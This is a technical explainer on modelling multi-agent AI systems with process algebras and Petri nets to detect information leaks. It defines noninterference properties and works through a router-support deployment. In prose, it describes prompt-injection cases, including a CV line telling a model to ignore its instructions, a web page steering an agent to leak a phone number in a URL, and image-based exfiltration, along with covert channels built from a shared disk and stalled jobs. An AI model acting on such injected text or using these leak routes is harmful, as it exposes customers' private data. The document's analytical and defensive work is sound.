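# Process algebras and Petri nets for checking information flow among AI agents

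## AI agents as communicating processes

Process algebras are small formal languages for describing systems whose parts run at the same time and exchange messages. The two classic ones are Robin Milner's Calculus of Communicating Systems (CCS), from 1980, and Tony Hoare's Communicating Sequential Processes (CSP), which became a book in 1985. A description in either language lists what a component can do next, and what it can do after that, but not how it works inside. Petri nets, an older graphical notation, describe such systems using transitions that remove marks from some places and add marks to others.

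Since the 1990s, computer scientists have used process algebras and Petri nets to look for information leaks. They divide a system's actions into secret ones and ones an outsider can observe, then check whether the secret actions affect what the outsider sees. Their usual examples were shared disks, access controls and cryptographic protocols. The same question now arises for groups of AI agents, which read private records, browse the web and send mail. But a language model determines what these agents do next, and nobody has written down its behaviour in advance. Both methods start from a written description of the system, so it is not obvious that they apply to agents.

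### What an agent does

An AI agent is a language model that ordinary software runs in a loop. The model writes text, and the software carries out actions requested in that text and returns the results to the model as more text. *A Technical Taxonomy of LLM Agent Communication Protocols* (Sander, Gidey and colleagues, 2026) divides the loop into stages in which the agent receives a task, thinks by writing out a plan, acts, and observes the outcome, after which it may plan again. To act, the model typically writes a tool call, which is a snippet of JSON (a plain-text format for structured data) containing the name of a tool and the parameters to run it with. It sends messages to other agents the same way. In both cases the model only requests an action, and a separate program carries it out or blocks it.

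The Model Context Protocol standardises the traffic between an agent and its tools. It involves the model, the client (the software that runs the model) and a server that offers tools. Under the current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the client first sends a `tools/list` request and gets back a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its inputs. The model picks one, say `get_weather` with the location New York, and the client sends a `tools/call` request with that name and argument. The server runs the tool and returns a result, such as a line of text with a temperature of 72°F, which the client passes to the model. A server can add or withdraw tools while the agent runs and notify the client. It can also respond to a call with a request for more input, such as a confirmation from the user, and the client then repeats the call with that input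 attached.

Under the specification, clients "should" show the user a tool's inputs before calling it, to avoid malicious or accidental data loss, and a person "should" always be able to refuse a call. Because "should" marks a recommendation rather than a requirement, a client that does neither can still conform. Since the July 2026 release, each HTTP request carries the tool's name in a header, which a gateway can use to authorise calls without parsing the message (Model Context Protocol, 2026). By default, though, the header does not include the tool's arguments, which are more likely to contain a secret.

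Agent2Agent (A2A) covers communication between agents. Google published it in April 2025, and version 1.0 dates from March 2026. *A2A v1.0* (Ghumare, 2026) reduces it to four objects: an agent card, which advertises what an agent can do and where to reach it; a task, which is a unit of work with an identifier and a state; a message, which contains text, raw bytes, a link or structured data; and an artifact, which is the output of a task. A task passes through states such as submitted, working, input required and completed. The other agent is opaque to the client, which receives only the card, the task's identifier and the sequence of states, and never the agent's model, memory, tools or plan. This suits process algebra, which describes each component only from the outside.

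Both protocols specify the format of a message but not which data it may contain. Sander and colleagues compared nine agent protocols and listed privacy and policy enforcement among the open research gaps.

### How a tool becomes a way out

Prompt injection occurs when an agent follows text in the material it reads as if that text were an instruction. Suppose a recruiter uses a language model to score job applications, and one applicant has hidden a line in a CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate. The model may follow that line even though the recruiter supplied the CV as data.

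This example comes from David C of the UK National Cyber Security Centre, whose *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* also explains why the problem has lasted. A database engine treats commands and data differently, so programmers could fix the cause of the older SQL injection attacks. A language model receives commands and data together as one run of text and predicts what comes next. Training and formatting can make attacks less likely to succeed, but David C thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever fully fix the vulnerability. He therefore advises developers to assume that an attacker who gets text in front of an agent may be able to use its tools, and to focus mainly on ordinary, predictable software that limits what those tools can do.

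One of the tools is usually a web browser. Fetching a page also sends data out. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that the request gives the website the page's address, which websites commonly log. That address can contain private data, such as a phone number. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, describes an attack that exploits this by tricking a chatbot into displaying an image. To load the image, the software sends the attacker's server a request for an address containing the private data.

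Companies as well as criminals have planted such text. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud said in December 2026 that it would stop sending AI agents prompts that sought local data and operating instructions, which it had used as part of its measures against abuse.

### The support deployment

*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, identifies customer service as one of the fields in which agents already work. A company that sells home routers, for example, might use three agents to answer its customers' questions.

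Each agent has one tool. The records agent can look up a customer's name, address, phone number, purchases and past complaints. The web agent can fetch web pages, because manufacturers' sites often explain what an error code means. The mail agent can send mail to people outside the company. Three message channels connect the agents. The records agent sends draft replies to the mail agent on one and queries to the web agent on another, and the web agent returns its findings on the third. The system must follow one rule, which is that customer data may leave the company only in replies that a person has approved.

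An outsider sees outgoing mail, including its recipient and text, and web requests, including their full addresses. It is safest to assume a single observer who sees all of both. This observer cannot see database lookups, messages between the agents or the moment of approval, which all happen inside the company. We also assume that the observer cannot see response times, which is a risky simplification. Outsiders write much of the incoming data, namely the web pages.

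Suppose the web agent fetches a page about an error code, and the page advises the reader to repeat the search with the customer's phone number added "to find the right firmware". The web agent includes this advice in its findings. The records agent follows it and puts the number in its next query. The web agent turns that query into a request to the site that the page recommended, with the number in the address. Each tool has worked as intended, no mail has gone out, and nobody has had anything to approve.

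Willison calls the dangerous combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to text from strangers, and a way to send data out. An auditor who checked the three agents one at a time might miss it. The records agent has access to the private data but cannot send it out. The web agent reads text from strangers and can send data out, but it has no access to the database. Once these two agents can exchange messages, together they have all three elements, which is the main reason to use a method that checks the whole system.

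OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a defence at this point. It tries to detect when a request would pass information from the conversation to a third party, then either asks the user to confirm or blocks the request. This is close to the support deployment's rule, applied to web requests. However, it relies on detection, and the attacker can choose how to disguise the phone number. A description of the whole system lets us ask about every route that exists, not just the requests that look suspicious.

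### The notation

*Classification of Security Properties* (Focardi and Gorrieri, 2001) sets out the Security Process Algebra, a version of Milner's CCS in which every visible action is either high or low. High actions involve secret data, while low actions are those an outside observer can see. In the support deployment, the low actions are `mail` and `fetch`. The high actions are looking up a record, passing a draft, a query or findings between agents, and approving a reply. The algebra also has one internal action, τ (tau), which nobody outside a process can observe.

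A visible action has two halves, one for the sender and one for the receiver. Focardi and Gorrieri put a bar over the sender's half, but in typed text it is easier to write `draft!` for sending a draft and `draft?` for receiving one.

A process describes what a component can do next. The simplest is `0`, which can do nothing. All others are built with a handful of operators, each defined by a rule about which steps the resulting process can take.

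Prefix, written `a.E`, puts an action `a` in front of a process `E`. The resulting process can only do `a` first, and then it behaves as `E`.

Choice, written `E + F`, can take any first step that `E` or `F` can take. After that step, the other branch is no longer available. The notation does not specify whether the choice is made by the component itself or by whatever it is communicating with.

In the parallel composition `E | F`, either process can take a step while the other stays where it is. If one can send on a channel on which the other can receive, both can also move together in a single indivisible step, a τ, which nobody else observes.

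Restriction, `E \ L`, removes every step of the process `E` whose action is in the set `L`, at every point in its run. Hiding, `E / L`, keeps those steps but relabels their actions as τ. Restricting the high actions therefore leaves the system with no secret activity, while hiding them lets the secret activity continue out of an outsider's sight.

The records agent and the mail agent now fit on a line each, and a third line connects them:

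```
Records = lookup!.record?.draft!.Records
Mail    = draft?.approve?.mail!.Mail
Desk    = (Records | Mail) \ {draft}
```

The records agent calls its lookup tool, receives a record, sends a draft and starts again. The mail agent receives a draft, waits for a person's approval, sends the mail and starts again. The database and the person are not part of the model; they supply the other halves of `lookup`, `record` and `approve` from outside. The restriction in the third line makes `draft` a private channel. Neither agent can now send or receive a draft on its own, so the only thing left is the joint step, which is a τ and which the ban does not touch. One complete exchange runs as follows:

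```
(Records | Mail) \ {draft}
   --lookup!-->    (record?.draft!.Records | Mail) \ {draft}
   --record?-->    (draft!.Records | Mail) \ {draft}
   --τ-->          (Records | approve?.mail!.Mail) \ {draft}
   --approve?-->   (Records | mail!.Mail) \ {draft}
   --mail!-->      (Records | Mail) \ {draft}
```

Each line follows from the one above by the step rules alone. Other orders are possible, because after the τ the records agent is free again and can look up the next customer before anyone has approved the first reply. However, it cannot hand over a second draft until the mail agent has finished with the first. This is a modelling decision. In Agent2Agent, as Ghumare explains, the call that sends a message does not return by default until the task ends or stops for input. To model this, one could add a second handshake, `done`, which the mail agent offers after sending and the records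 agent waits for.

The reachable states and the steps between them form a labelled transition system, which consists of a set of states, one of them the starting state, and arrows labelled with action names. `Records` and `Mail` have three states each, and every combination is reachable, so `Desk` has nine states and thirteen arrows. Checking programs work on this system. *μACP* (2026), a calculus for communication between agents, skips the algebra at this point and defines an agent directly as a labelled transition system with finitely many states. The algebra is useful when there are many components, because the diagram can grow exponentially with their number while the text grows by one line for each.

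If `High` is the set of all high actions, `Desk \ High` cannot take any step, because its first step would be a lookup. `Desk / High` can send mail repeatedly, with some unobservable steps before each message. Noninterference, the requirement that high activity makes no difference to what a low observer can see, is based on comparing two such versions of a system.

### Messages with something in them

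So far a draft is just a draft, with no text. To follow customer data the actions need contents, and Focardi and Gorrieri add them in a value-passing version of the language. Here are a records agent that can also consult the web, and the web agent, without the findings that come back:

```
Records = lookup!.record?(x).(draft!(x).Records + query!(x).Records)
Web     = query?(y).fetch!(y).Web
```

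If these run in parallel with a mail agent that passes its drafts on in the same way, and `draft` and `query` are restricted, the system can perform the sequence `lookup!`, `record?(x)`, `fetch!(x)`. The record then goes out in a web request, and the sequence contains no approval.

Focardi and Gorrieri introduce value-passing with a buffer cell that takes in a number and outputs the same number. They remark that the flow is legitimate when the input is low and the output high. With a high input and a low output, the cell is insecure because it moves information down. `Web`, like any web agent that receives queries from inside and sends requests outside, is a buffer cell of this insecure kind, whichever model runs it.

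In theory, message contents need no new machinery. An action with a variable in it is shorthand for a family of plain actions, one for each value the variable can take, and an input becomes a choice among all of them. In practice, a program can check the model only if these families are finite and small. A ten-digit phone number already gives ten billion versions of `fetch`. The usual solution is to restrict `x` to 0 or 1. A one-bit leak in this small model is a concern for the real system too, since an attacker who can extract one bit can generally repeat the attack to get more. It is harder to conclude that the real system is secure because the small model has no leak. That requires showing that the components handle all values in the same way, which a language model plainly does not do with text.

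Focardi and Gorrieri's main example is an access monitor, which is structured much like a tool server. It controls access to two one-bit variables, one high and one low, and handles requests from high and low users. Low users may not read the high variable, and high users may not write to the low one. To store a 1 in the low variable, a low user performs `access_w(0,0)`, a write request from level 0 for object 0, and then `write(0,1)`, which supplies the value 1. The monitor then passes the value to the variable in a τ step, which, unlike the first two steps, is invisible. If a high user asks to write to the low variable, the monitor accepts the request and the value but ignores both and gives no error message.

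### When two processes count as the same

Every check in this field ultimately tests whether an observer can tell two processes apart, and the result depends on which differences the observer can detect.

The least demanding test compares traces. A trace is a finite sequence of visible actions that a process can perform, with any τ steps left out. The exchange above has the trace `lookup!`, `record?`, `approve?`, `mail!`, and each of its prefixes, including the empty one, is also a trace. Two processes are trace equivalent if they have the same set of traces. People who work on agents already use a similar notion. Dantas and colleagues define an agent's plan as a finite sequence of actions from its tool set, and the safety properties they consider are conditions on a single such sequence.

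Traces miss something. Compare these two processes, with the final `0`s left out:

```
E = a.b + a.c
F = a.(b + c)
```

`E` and `F` have identical traces, since each can do `a` then `b`, or `a` then `c`. But doing `a` puts `E` either in a state where only `b` is possible or in one where only `c` is, while `F` can still do either after `a`.

If `c` is now forbidden, `F \ {c}` does `a` and can always go on to `b`, but `E \ {c}` may do `a`, enter the branch that needs `c` and get stuck. The two restricted processes still have the same traces, which are the empty trace, `a`, and `a` followed by `b`, because a trace doesn't record what a process was unable to do next.

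In the support deployment, `a` could be the arrival of a draft, `b` sending it, and `c` handing the case to a member of staff through a ticket system. After reading the draft, a mail agent like `F` can still do either, while one like `E` has already committed to one of them. Such early commitment is quite plausible when a language model makes the decision, since the same input can lead to different decisions on different runs. If the ticket system goes down, `F` still sends its mail, but `E` does nothing on the runs where it has chosen the handover, and the customer waiting for an answer can notice this.

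Weak bisimilarity is the stricter test that tells `E` from `F`. Informally, two processes are weakly bisimilar if they can match each other's steps for ever, internal steps being ignored. Exactly, a relation between processes is a weak bisimulation if, whenever it pairs some `P` with some `Q`, two conditions hold:

- for every step that `P` can take to some `P′`, `Q` can answer with the same action, with any number of τ steps before and after it, and arrive at some `Q′` that the relation pairs with `P′`;
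- for every step that `Q` can take, `P` can answer in the same way.

If the step is a τ, the other side may match it with any number of τ steps, including none. `P` and `Q` are weakly bisimilar if some weak bisimulation pairs them.

`E` and `F` are not bisimilar. When `F` does `a`, it becomes `b + c`, and `E` can match that step only by moving to `b` or to `c`. If `E` moves to `b`, it cannot match `F` doing `c` next. If it moves to `c`, it cannot match `F` doing `b`.

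`Desk / High`, the nine-state system with its secret steps hidden, is weakly bisimilar to the one-line process `M = mail!.M`. The relation that shows this pairs each of the nine states with `M`. When the desk takes a hidden step, `M` stays in the same state. When the desk sends mail, `M` does too. When `M` sends mail, the desk can always send mail as well, possibly after a few hidden steps. Weakly bisimilar processes always have the same traces, but processes with the same traces need not be weakly bisimilar, as `E` and `F` show.

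### What CSP and the pi-calculus add

Hoare's CSP addresses the weakness of traces differently, by recording refusals, the sets of actions that a process may be unable to perform after each trace. `E \ {c}` can refuse `b` after `a`, and `F \ {c}` cannot, so CSP also distinguishes them. Refusals and weak bisimilarity sometimes disagree. `a.b.c + a.b.d` and `a.(b.c + b.d)` have the same refusals but are not weakly bisimilar. Conversely, weak bisimilarity equates `a.b` with a process that, after `a`, can do `b` but can also take internal steps forever without doing `b`, whereas CSP distinguishes the two. An agent that keeps revising its plan and never acts would be a real example of the second process. Focardi and Gorrieri nonetheless chose weak bisimilarity for their security properties because they found the way refusals handle endless internal activity unsuitable for this purpose.

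In CCS, a component cannot acquire new channels. The pi-calculus, which Milner and others published in 1992, removes this limit by letting processes send channel names to each other. *We are currently clean on OPSEC* (2026), which uses the calculus to model how officials handle secrets, gives the central rule that a process receiving a name substitutes it for a variable throughout the rest of its description. For example, the process `announce?(t).t!(x).0` receives a channel name `t` on the channel `announce`, then sends `x` on the channel it received. A later extension, the applied pi-calculus, adds functions and equations on the data, and researchers have used it to model security protocols, according to *Modeling Quantum Computing with π-calculus* (2026).

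The pi-calculus lets processes send each other channel names, which suits agents rather well because a Model Context Protocol server can announce a new tool in the middle of a run. Sending names also raises the question of whether knowing a name is enough to use the channel, which is easy to overlook when channels are fixed. It is enough in the pi-calculus, but in the Model Context Protocol it depends on the server. Some tools return a handle, a short string that identifies, say, a shopping basket, and the model passes the string back in later calls. The specification advises servers that authenticate their callers to treat a handle as only a name and to check the caller's authority on every call. If a server doesn't authenticate callers, anyone who has the string can use it, as in the pi-calculus. An agent that leaks such a handle in a web address then gives away the channel along with the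 data.

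## Noninterference as a comparison of two processes

Most systems protect secret data with access rules, which set who may read and write what. In multilevel security, a strict version, every user and file has a level, and no user can change two rules: nobody may read from a higher level, and nobody may write to a lower one. Focardi and Gorrieri give an example of a leak that breaks neither rule. A program at a high level and one at a low level share a hard disk. The high program fills the disk to send a 1 and frees some space to send a 0. The low program keeps trying to write, and takes each "disk full" error as a 1 and each successful write as a 0.

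The support deployment could leak in the same way. Suppose the records agent and the web agent share a disk for their working files, and the web agent stores a copy of each page it fetches. If the disk is full, the web agent can't store the copy and has to fetch the page again the next time it needs it. A records agent that has followed a malicious instruction can fill the disk or leave it alone, depending on one bit of the customer's phone number. When the web agent needs a page twice, the website's owner sees two requests if the disk is full and one if it isn't. The requested addresses contain no customer data, and the records agent has sent the web agent no query.

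Security researchers call such a path a covert channel. A list of rules for known channels will miss the channels that nobody has thought of. Noninterference instead requires that high activity make no difference to what the outsider sees, by any route.

### Deleting the secret actions

Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, introduced the idea. The test is to take any sequence of actions, delete the high ones and run the system again. If low users get the same outputs both times, the high users do not interfere with them. For a machine that gives exactly one output for each action, van der Meyden and Zhang (2008), in *A Comparison of Semantic Models for Noninterference*, write this as an equation, here in slightly simpler notation:

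```
out(s0 · α, a) = out(s0 · purge(α), a)
```

Here `s0` is the starting state, `s0 · α` is the state after the sequence of actions `α`, and `purge(α)` is `α` without its high actions. The equation must hold for every `α` and every low action `a`. The shared disk violates this condition. Suppose `α` is the single high action of filling the disk and `a` is a low write. On the left side of the equation, the output is an error message. On the right side, `purge(α)` is empty, so the disk has space and the write succeeds.

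The equation only makes sense if each input has one possible output. Agents that run at the same time can interleave their steps in many orders, and a language model can respond to the same input in different ways. For such a system, we have to compare everything it can do when high actions can occur to everything it can do without them.

### Two versions of one system

Focardi and Gorrieri make this comparison with restriction and hiding. A system `E` is secure if a low observer cannot tell `E \ High`, with the high actions forbidden, from `E / High`, with them hidden. With trace equivalence, this property is strong nondeterministic noninterference (SNNI). With weak bisimilarity, it is BSNNI:

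```
SNNI:    E \ High  and  E / High  are trace equivalent
BSNNI:   E \ High  and  E / High  are weakly bisimilar
```

For traces, this is essentially the 1982 test. A process satisfies SNNI exactly when deleting the high actions from any of its traces leaves a sequence that is also one of its traces.

Take an agent that reads a secret bit and sends it out, where the reads are high and the sends are low:

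```
Forward = read0.send0 + read1.send1
```

`Forward \ High` can do nothing, because both possible first steps are high. `Forward / High` is `τ.send0 + τ.send1`, which has the traces `send0` and `send1`. So the agent fails SNNI. It would also fail if it sent the same message in both cases, since anyone who received the message would know that a read had happened. SNNI requires the agent to hide whether something secret happened, as well as the secret value.

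Noninterference is too strict for the support deployment as a whole. `Desk` from the previous section fails because it can send mail only after high actions, even though those mails are approved replies that the company wants to send. Permitted release needs a weaker definition, which comes later. Noninterference is the right requirement only for parts of the deployment that should release nothing, such as the web requests.

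A system passes if nothing leads from its high actions to its low ones. Suppose one agent only looks up records, while another only fetches a manufacturer's public status page:

```
Archive = lookup!.record?.Archive
Watch   = fetch!.Watch
Apart   = Archive | Watch
```

The second agent keeps fetching in both `Apart \ High` and `Apart / High`. The first agent is stuck at its first step in `Apart \ High` and takes τ steps forever in `Apart / High`. Both processes are weakly bisimilar to `Watch`, so `Apart` satisfies BSNNI.

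A check based on CSP's refusals would wrongly fail `Apart`, which has no leak. Only the hidden version can take internal steps forever, so the check would treat the two versions as different. Focardi and Gorrieri also found the opposite error. After they added an endless internal backup routine to a system that a high user could halt, the refusal-based check no longer detected the problem.

### A status mail that never arrives

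When we hide the high actions, we assume that someone is always ready to take part in them. An attacker can do more harm by taking part in one high action and refusing the next.

Suppose the company sends a distributor a status mail every evening. The mail agent can send it straight away, or it can first take part in a maintenance job on the customer database, which begins and ends with a high action:

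```
Status = mail! + begin?.end?.mail!
```

*Noninterference Analysis of Reversible Systems* (Esposito, Aldini and colleagues, 2025) uses the same process as an example, with different names: `l + h1.h2.l`. With its high actions forbidden, `Status` is `mail!`. With them hidden, it is `mail! + τ.τ.mail!`, which is weakly bisimilar to `mail!` because the mail can still go out after either τ. So `Status` satisfies BSNNI.

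The high process `Stall = begin!.0` begins the job and never ends it. Combined with `Status`, it gives the system `(Status | Stall) \ High`, which can either send the mail or take a τ, in which the job begins, and then wait for an `end` that never comes. The system therefore behaves like `mail! + τ.0`. The process `mail!` cannot match that τ, because it can only stay where it is, still able to send mail, while the stalled system cannot send any. A distributor who gets no mail therefore learns something about the database.

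To detect such cases, Focardi and Gorrieri compare the system with what it becomes when any high process at all is attached. This gives non-deducibility on compositions, or NDC, and its bisimulation-based form, BNDC:

```
NDC:    E / High  and  (E | P) \ High  are trace equivalent,   for every high process P
BNDC:   E / High  and  (E | P) \ High  are weakly bisimilar,   for every high process P
```

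A high process is one whose visible actions are all high. `P` might be a program planted by an attacker, or a language model that has read an attacker's text. You can apply BNDC without describing what `P` does, which is the main reason to consider it for agents whose behaviour is not fixed in advance.

### Which property implies which

The properties form a chain, from strictest to weakest:

```
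BNDC  ⇒  BSNNI  ⇒  SNNI  ⇔  NDC
```

BNDC implies BSNNI because one of the high processes we can attach is `0`, which does nothing, and attaching it has the same effect as forbidding the high actions. `Status` is a counterexample to the converse. BSNNI implies SNNI because weakly bisimilar processes have the same traces.

The last equivalence in the chain is more surprising. On traces, testing `E` with every possible attacker reveals nothing that the simple comparison would miss. Focardi and Gorrieri's proof depends on two inclusions. Every trace of `E \ High` is also a trace of `(E | P) \ High`, since the attacker `P` may stay idle. Every trace of `(E | P) \ High` is in turn a trace of `E / High`, since hiding lets `E` take its high steps without a partner. So if `E \ High` and `E / High` have the same traces, `(E | P) \ High` must have them too. The argument does not work for bisimilarity,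 where an extra dead end makes a difference even if it adds no trace. For example, `mail!` and `mail! + τ.0` have the same traces but are not bisimilar, because only the second can stop without sending.

Van der Meyden and Zhang prove a similar result for state machines. In an asynchronous system, where high actions can always be delayed, a high user who picks each action in response to what has happened so far can reveal no more than one who follows a fixed list. An example by Wittbold and Johnson shows that a responsive high user can reveal more in a synchronous system, where everyone acts at once. Van der Meyden and Zhang's machines also accept every action at all times, so no one can stall them by withholding `end`. Agents and their tools, however, wait for each other, for approvals and for results, so they can be blocked.

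BNDC is hard to check because there are infinitely many high processes to attach. Focardi and Gorrieri therefore propose a stricter property, SBSNNI, which requires every reachable state to satisfy BSNNI. It implies BNDC, and its definition involves no attacker. `Status` fails SBSNNI because of the state after `begin`, `end?.mail!`, which can do nothing when high actions are forbidden but can send mail when they are hidden.

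Some systems satisfy BNDC but fail this stricter check. Bossi, Focardi and colleagues, in *Bisimulation and Unwinding for Verifying Possibilistic Security Properties*, repair a process much like `Status` by giving it an innocent way to fail. Applied to the status mail, their repair gives

```
Flaky = τ.mail! + τ.0 + begin?.end?.mail!
```

The mail now sometimes fails to go out for internal reasons, so a missing mail no longer proves that a job began, and `Flaky` satisfies BNDC. The state after `begin` is still as bad as before, so `Flaky` fails SBSNNI. Bossi and colleagues argue that this matters when a process might move to a new environment mid-run. An agent paused after `begin` and resumed elsewhere would start from that state.

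### Five versions of an access monitor

Focardi and Gorrieri tested their definitions on the access monitor from the previous section, which handles read and write requests for one high and one low variable. They built several versions of the monitor, most with a deliberate flaw. The table also includes their first property, NNI, which uses traces and forbids only high inputs.

| Version | NNI | SNNI | BSNNI | BNDC |
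|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Enforces both access rules | passes | passes | passes | fails |
| 2. Does not check writes | fails | fails | fails | fails |
| 3. Notifies high users when a low user writes to the high variable | passes | fails | fails | fails |
| 4. Lets a high user stop the monitor | passes | passes | fails | fails |
| 5. Version 1 with buffers and one-step writes | passes | passes | passes | passes |

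In version 2, a high user can write a 1 into the low variable, which starts at 0, and a low user can then read it. In traces without high inputs, a low user can read a 1 there only if a low user has written it, so even the weakest property detects the flaw.

Version 3 leaks because the monitor cannot continue until a high user accepts a notice. A low user who writes twice therefore knows that a high user accepted the first notice. NNI does not detect this because the notice is an output. Focardi and Gorrieri concluded that when both sides must take part in a communication, outputs can leak as easily as inputs. The leak depends on modelling notices this way, and would disappear if they went into a mailbox that never refused them. Van der Meyden and Zhang warn about this kind of modelling choice. In their state machines a user cannot refuse an observation, while process algebra usually treats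 it as an action that the user can decline.

Version 1 of the monitor looked secure until Focardi and Gorrieri attached a high user that asked to read a variable and never collected the answer. The monitor then waits forever, and low users get no service. A high user can also block the monitor by announcing a write and withholding the value. Version 5 prevents both problems by putting the answer in a buffer and accepting a write request and its value in a single step.

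Focardi and Gorrieri showed that stalled monitors can leak data reliably, even though a low user who gets no answer can never be sure that one will not still come. They built a channel from three copies of version 1. The sender freezes copies 0 and 1 by announcing writes, then frees the copy whose number matches the bit it wants to send by supplying that copy's missing value. The receiver tries to read from both copies and learns the bit from the one that responds. The third copy signals when a bit is ready, and two permitted channels from low to high signal the sender to continue. After some random output at the start, the arrangement is a perfect one-bit channel.

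An attacker inside the company can use the status mail in the same way if the company sends two, say one for each region. The attacker begins a job for each mail and ends only one of the jobs. The distributor can then read the bit from which mail arrives, without a clock or a deadline.

### Checking by machine

Focardi and Gorrieri wrote a program called the Compositional Security Checker (CoSeC) to make these comparisons. The user supplies a system description in the Security Process Algebra and a list of high actions. CoSeC builds the two processes as labelled transition systems and tests whether they are equivalent. If a trace property fails, CoSeC can show a trace that only one process has. If SBSNNI fails, it returns an insecure reachable state. For version 1 of the monitor, it returned a state in which the monitor held an answer for a high user, and Focardi and Gorrieri could easily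 work out the attack from that state.

Weak bisimilarity is stricter than trace equivalence but easier to check. The time needed to check it grows as a polynomial in the number of states, while trace equivalence is PSPACE-complete, so the known methods for checking it can take exponential time. The number of states is the larger problem for both. Four processes of three states each combined to give 81 states, which CoSeC took about 270 seconds to check on a workstation of the time.

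CoSeC took about 16 minutes to check version 5 of the monitor. When Focardi and Gorrieri rebuilt the monitor from parts that were each secure, the check took about 20 seconds, because SBSNNI carries over from the parts to the whole. Fabio Martinelli showed that BNDC does not carry over in this way. He also proved that BNDC is decidable for systems with finitely many states, and wrote a verifier that can construct an interfering high process. Petri nets can have infinitely many states, so his proof does not cover all of them. Bossi and colleagues, who call SBSNNI persistent BNDC, later found polynomial methods for checking it that are faster than CoSeC's.

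These numbers are small by today's standards. `Desk` has only nine states because we described each agent in a single line. The check applies to those descriptions and does not establish whether a real agent follows them.

### Why a list of allowed runs is not enough

Many safety rules amount to a list of allowed runs. "No mail without an approval" is one, since we can look at any single run and say whether it breaks the rule. Noninterference is not such a rule, as two very small processes show:

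```
Either = send + read.send
Only   = read.send
```

`Either` is secure because it can send with or without a read, so an outsider who sees a message learns nothing about the read, whatever high process is attached. `Only` is insecure because an outsider who sees a message knows that a read took place. But every run of `Only` is also a run of `Either`, so any list of allowed runs that accepts `Either` must also accept `Only`.

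`Either` is secure because it can send without reading, even if it never does so in an actual run. Focardi and Gorrieri state the general requirement that if some behaviour can occur, some related behaviour must also be possible. A log of what a system did does not show whether it could have done something else. A program that watches one run at a time therefore cannot enforce noninterference exactly, though it may enforce a stricter rule that implies it.

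A secure system can therefore also become insecure when some of its possible behaviors are removed. *Mathematical Models of Computer Security* notes that the usual methods of turning a design into a program step by step work well for safety properties but tend not to preserve security. Suppose a web agent sometimes checks a status page after a customer lookup and sometimes without one. After an update, it stops making the checks that don't follow a lookup. Everything it does now was possible before, so every rule about single runs still holds, but each request to the status page now reveals a lookup.

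### Requiring a deterministic low view

Roscoe proposed a condition in CSP that avoids this problem. The system runs alongside a process that can perform any high action at any time, and the two do not communicate. An observer who sees a high action then cannot tell which of them performed it. The system is secure if the combination has no endless internal activity and is deterministic, meaning that after any given trace there is no action it might either accept or refuse.

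`Only` fails this test. After the trace `read`, the combination can send if `Only` did the reading, but not if the other process did. FDR, a model checker for CSP, can check the condition automatically.

Focardi and Gorrieri object that Roscoe's condition is too strict. The process `a.b + a.c` has three low actions and no high ones, so it has no secret to leak, but it fails the condition because it may accept or refuse `b` after `a`. They also proved that Roscoe's condition, BNDC and SBSNNI are equivalent for systems with deterministic low behaviour and no endless internal activity.

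The strictness has a benefit, though, which we can see by adding two branches to the forwarding agent:

```
Guess = read0.send0 + read1.send1 + τ.send0 + τ.send1
```

This agent either reads the secret bit and sends it, or makes up a bit and sends that. It satisfies SBSNNI and therefore BNDC, since every message it sends could have been made up. If it makes up only one bit in a thousand, the outsider still learns nearly everything, but none of these definitions accounts for how often each choice occurs. And if an update removes the guessing, the agent becomes `Forward`. Roscoe's condition rejects `Guess` from the start because it requires deterministic low behaviour, which leaves no such choices for an update to remove.

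A language model that words its mail differently on each run fails Roscoe's condition even if it has never received a secret. BNDC allows this variation, but it also accepts an agent that hides leaked secrets among details it makes up.

### When steps can be undone

Weak bisimilarity lets a process take any number of internal steps before it matches a visible one, regardless of the states it passes through. Esposito and colleagues argued in 2023, in the first submitted version of their paper, that this is too permissive for systems that can also run backwards.

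Their example is a health database that may pass a user's data to a machine-learning module for training. Users must not find out whether this has happened. They log in with a password, through single sign-on or with two factors, and only data from the last two methods may go into training. In the following version of their process, `train` is the high action and the logins are low:

```
Auth = password.Auth
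     + train.sso.Auth + train.twofactor.Auth
     + τ.(τ.sso.Auth + τ.twofactor.Auth)
```

The last line lets the database require a strong login without using the data, so a strong login doesn't reveal the training. This hides the training as long as the system only runs forwards, and `Auth` satisfies SBSNNI.

Suppose an error occurs just after a single sign-on, and a debugging tool undoes the login and the step before it. If that step was `train`, the database returns to the start and offers a password login again. If it was the decoy's second τ, the database returns to the middle of the decoy, where only the two strong methods are available, so the user can tell the two cases apart.

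Branching bisimilarity is a stricter equivalence that detects this. If one process takes internal steps before matching the other's move, the state it reaches just before the matching step must still be equivalent to the state the other is moving from. The decoy's middle state fails this requirement because it does not offer the password login. De Nicola, Montanari and Vaandrager had already proved that weak bisimilarity becomes branching bisimilarity when processes must also match each other's backward steps. Esposito and colleagues rebuilt the SNNI and BNDC family on branching bisimilarity and found that the properties imply one another in the same order as before. Branching bisimilarity is also faster to check than weak bisimilarity.

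They accept that the stricter test is too severe for systems that only run forwards, where the leak in `Auth` does not exist. The support deployment, as we have described it, cannot undo a step, so weak bisimilarity is enough. Its operators would need the stricter test if they added software that returned an agent to an earlier checkpoint after an error.

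## Information flow in Petri nets

The checks in the previous section all work on a labelled transition system, which needs a separate state for every combination of the agents' states. Ten agents with three states each can produce 59,049 combinations, and a support desk with no limit on waiting customers has infinitely many. A Petri net describes the same system without listing the combinations. This makes some leaks visible in the drawing of the net and makes it possible to check some systems with infinitely many states.

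### A net with four places

A Petri net consists of places and transitions, with arrows between them. Places hold marks, which most papers call tokens. An arrow from a place `p` to a transition `t` has a weight `F(p,t)`, the number of marks that `t` takes from `p`. An arrow from `t` to `p` has a weight `F(t,p)`, the number of marks that `t` puts into `p`. Where there is no arrow, the weight is 0. A marking `M` gives the number of marks in each place.

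A transition is enabled if every place holds at least as many marks as the transition takes from it. An enabled transition can fire, which changes the marking in a single step:

```
M′(p) = M(p) − F(p,t) + F(t,p)      for every place p
```

A marking is reachable if some sequence of firings leads to it from the starting marking.

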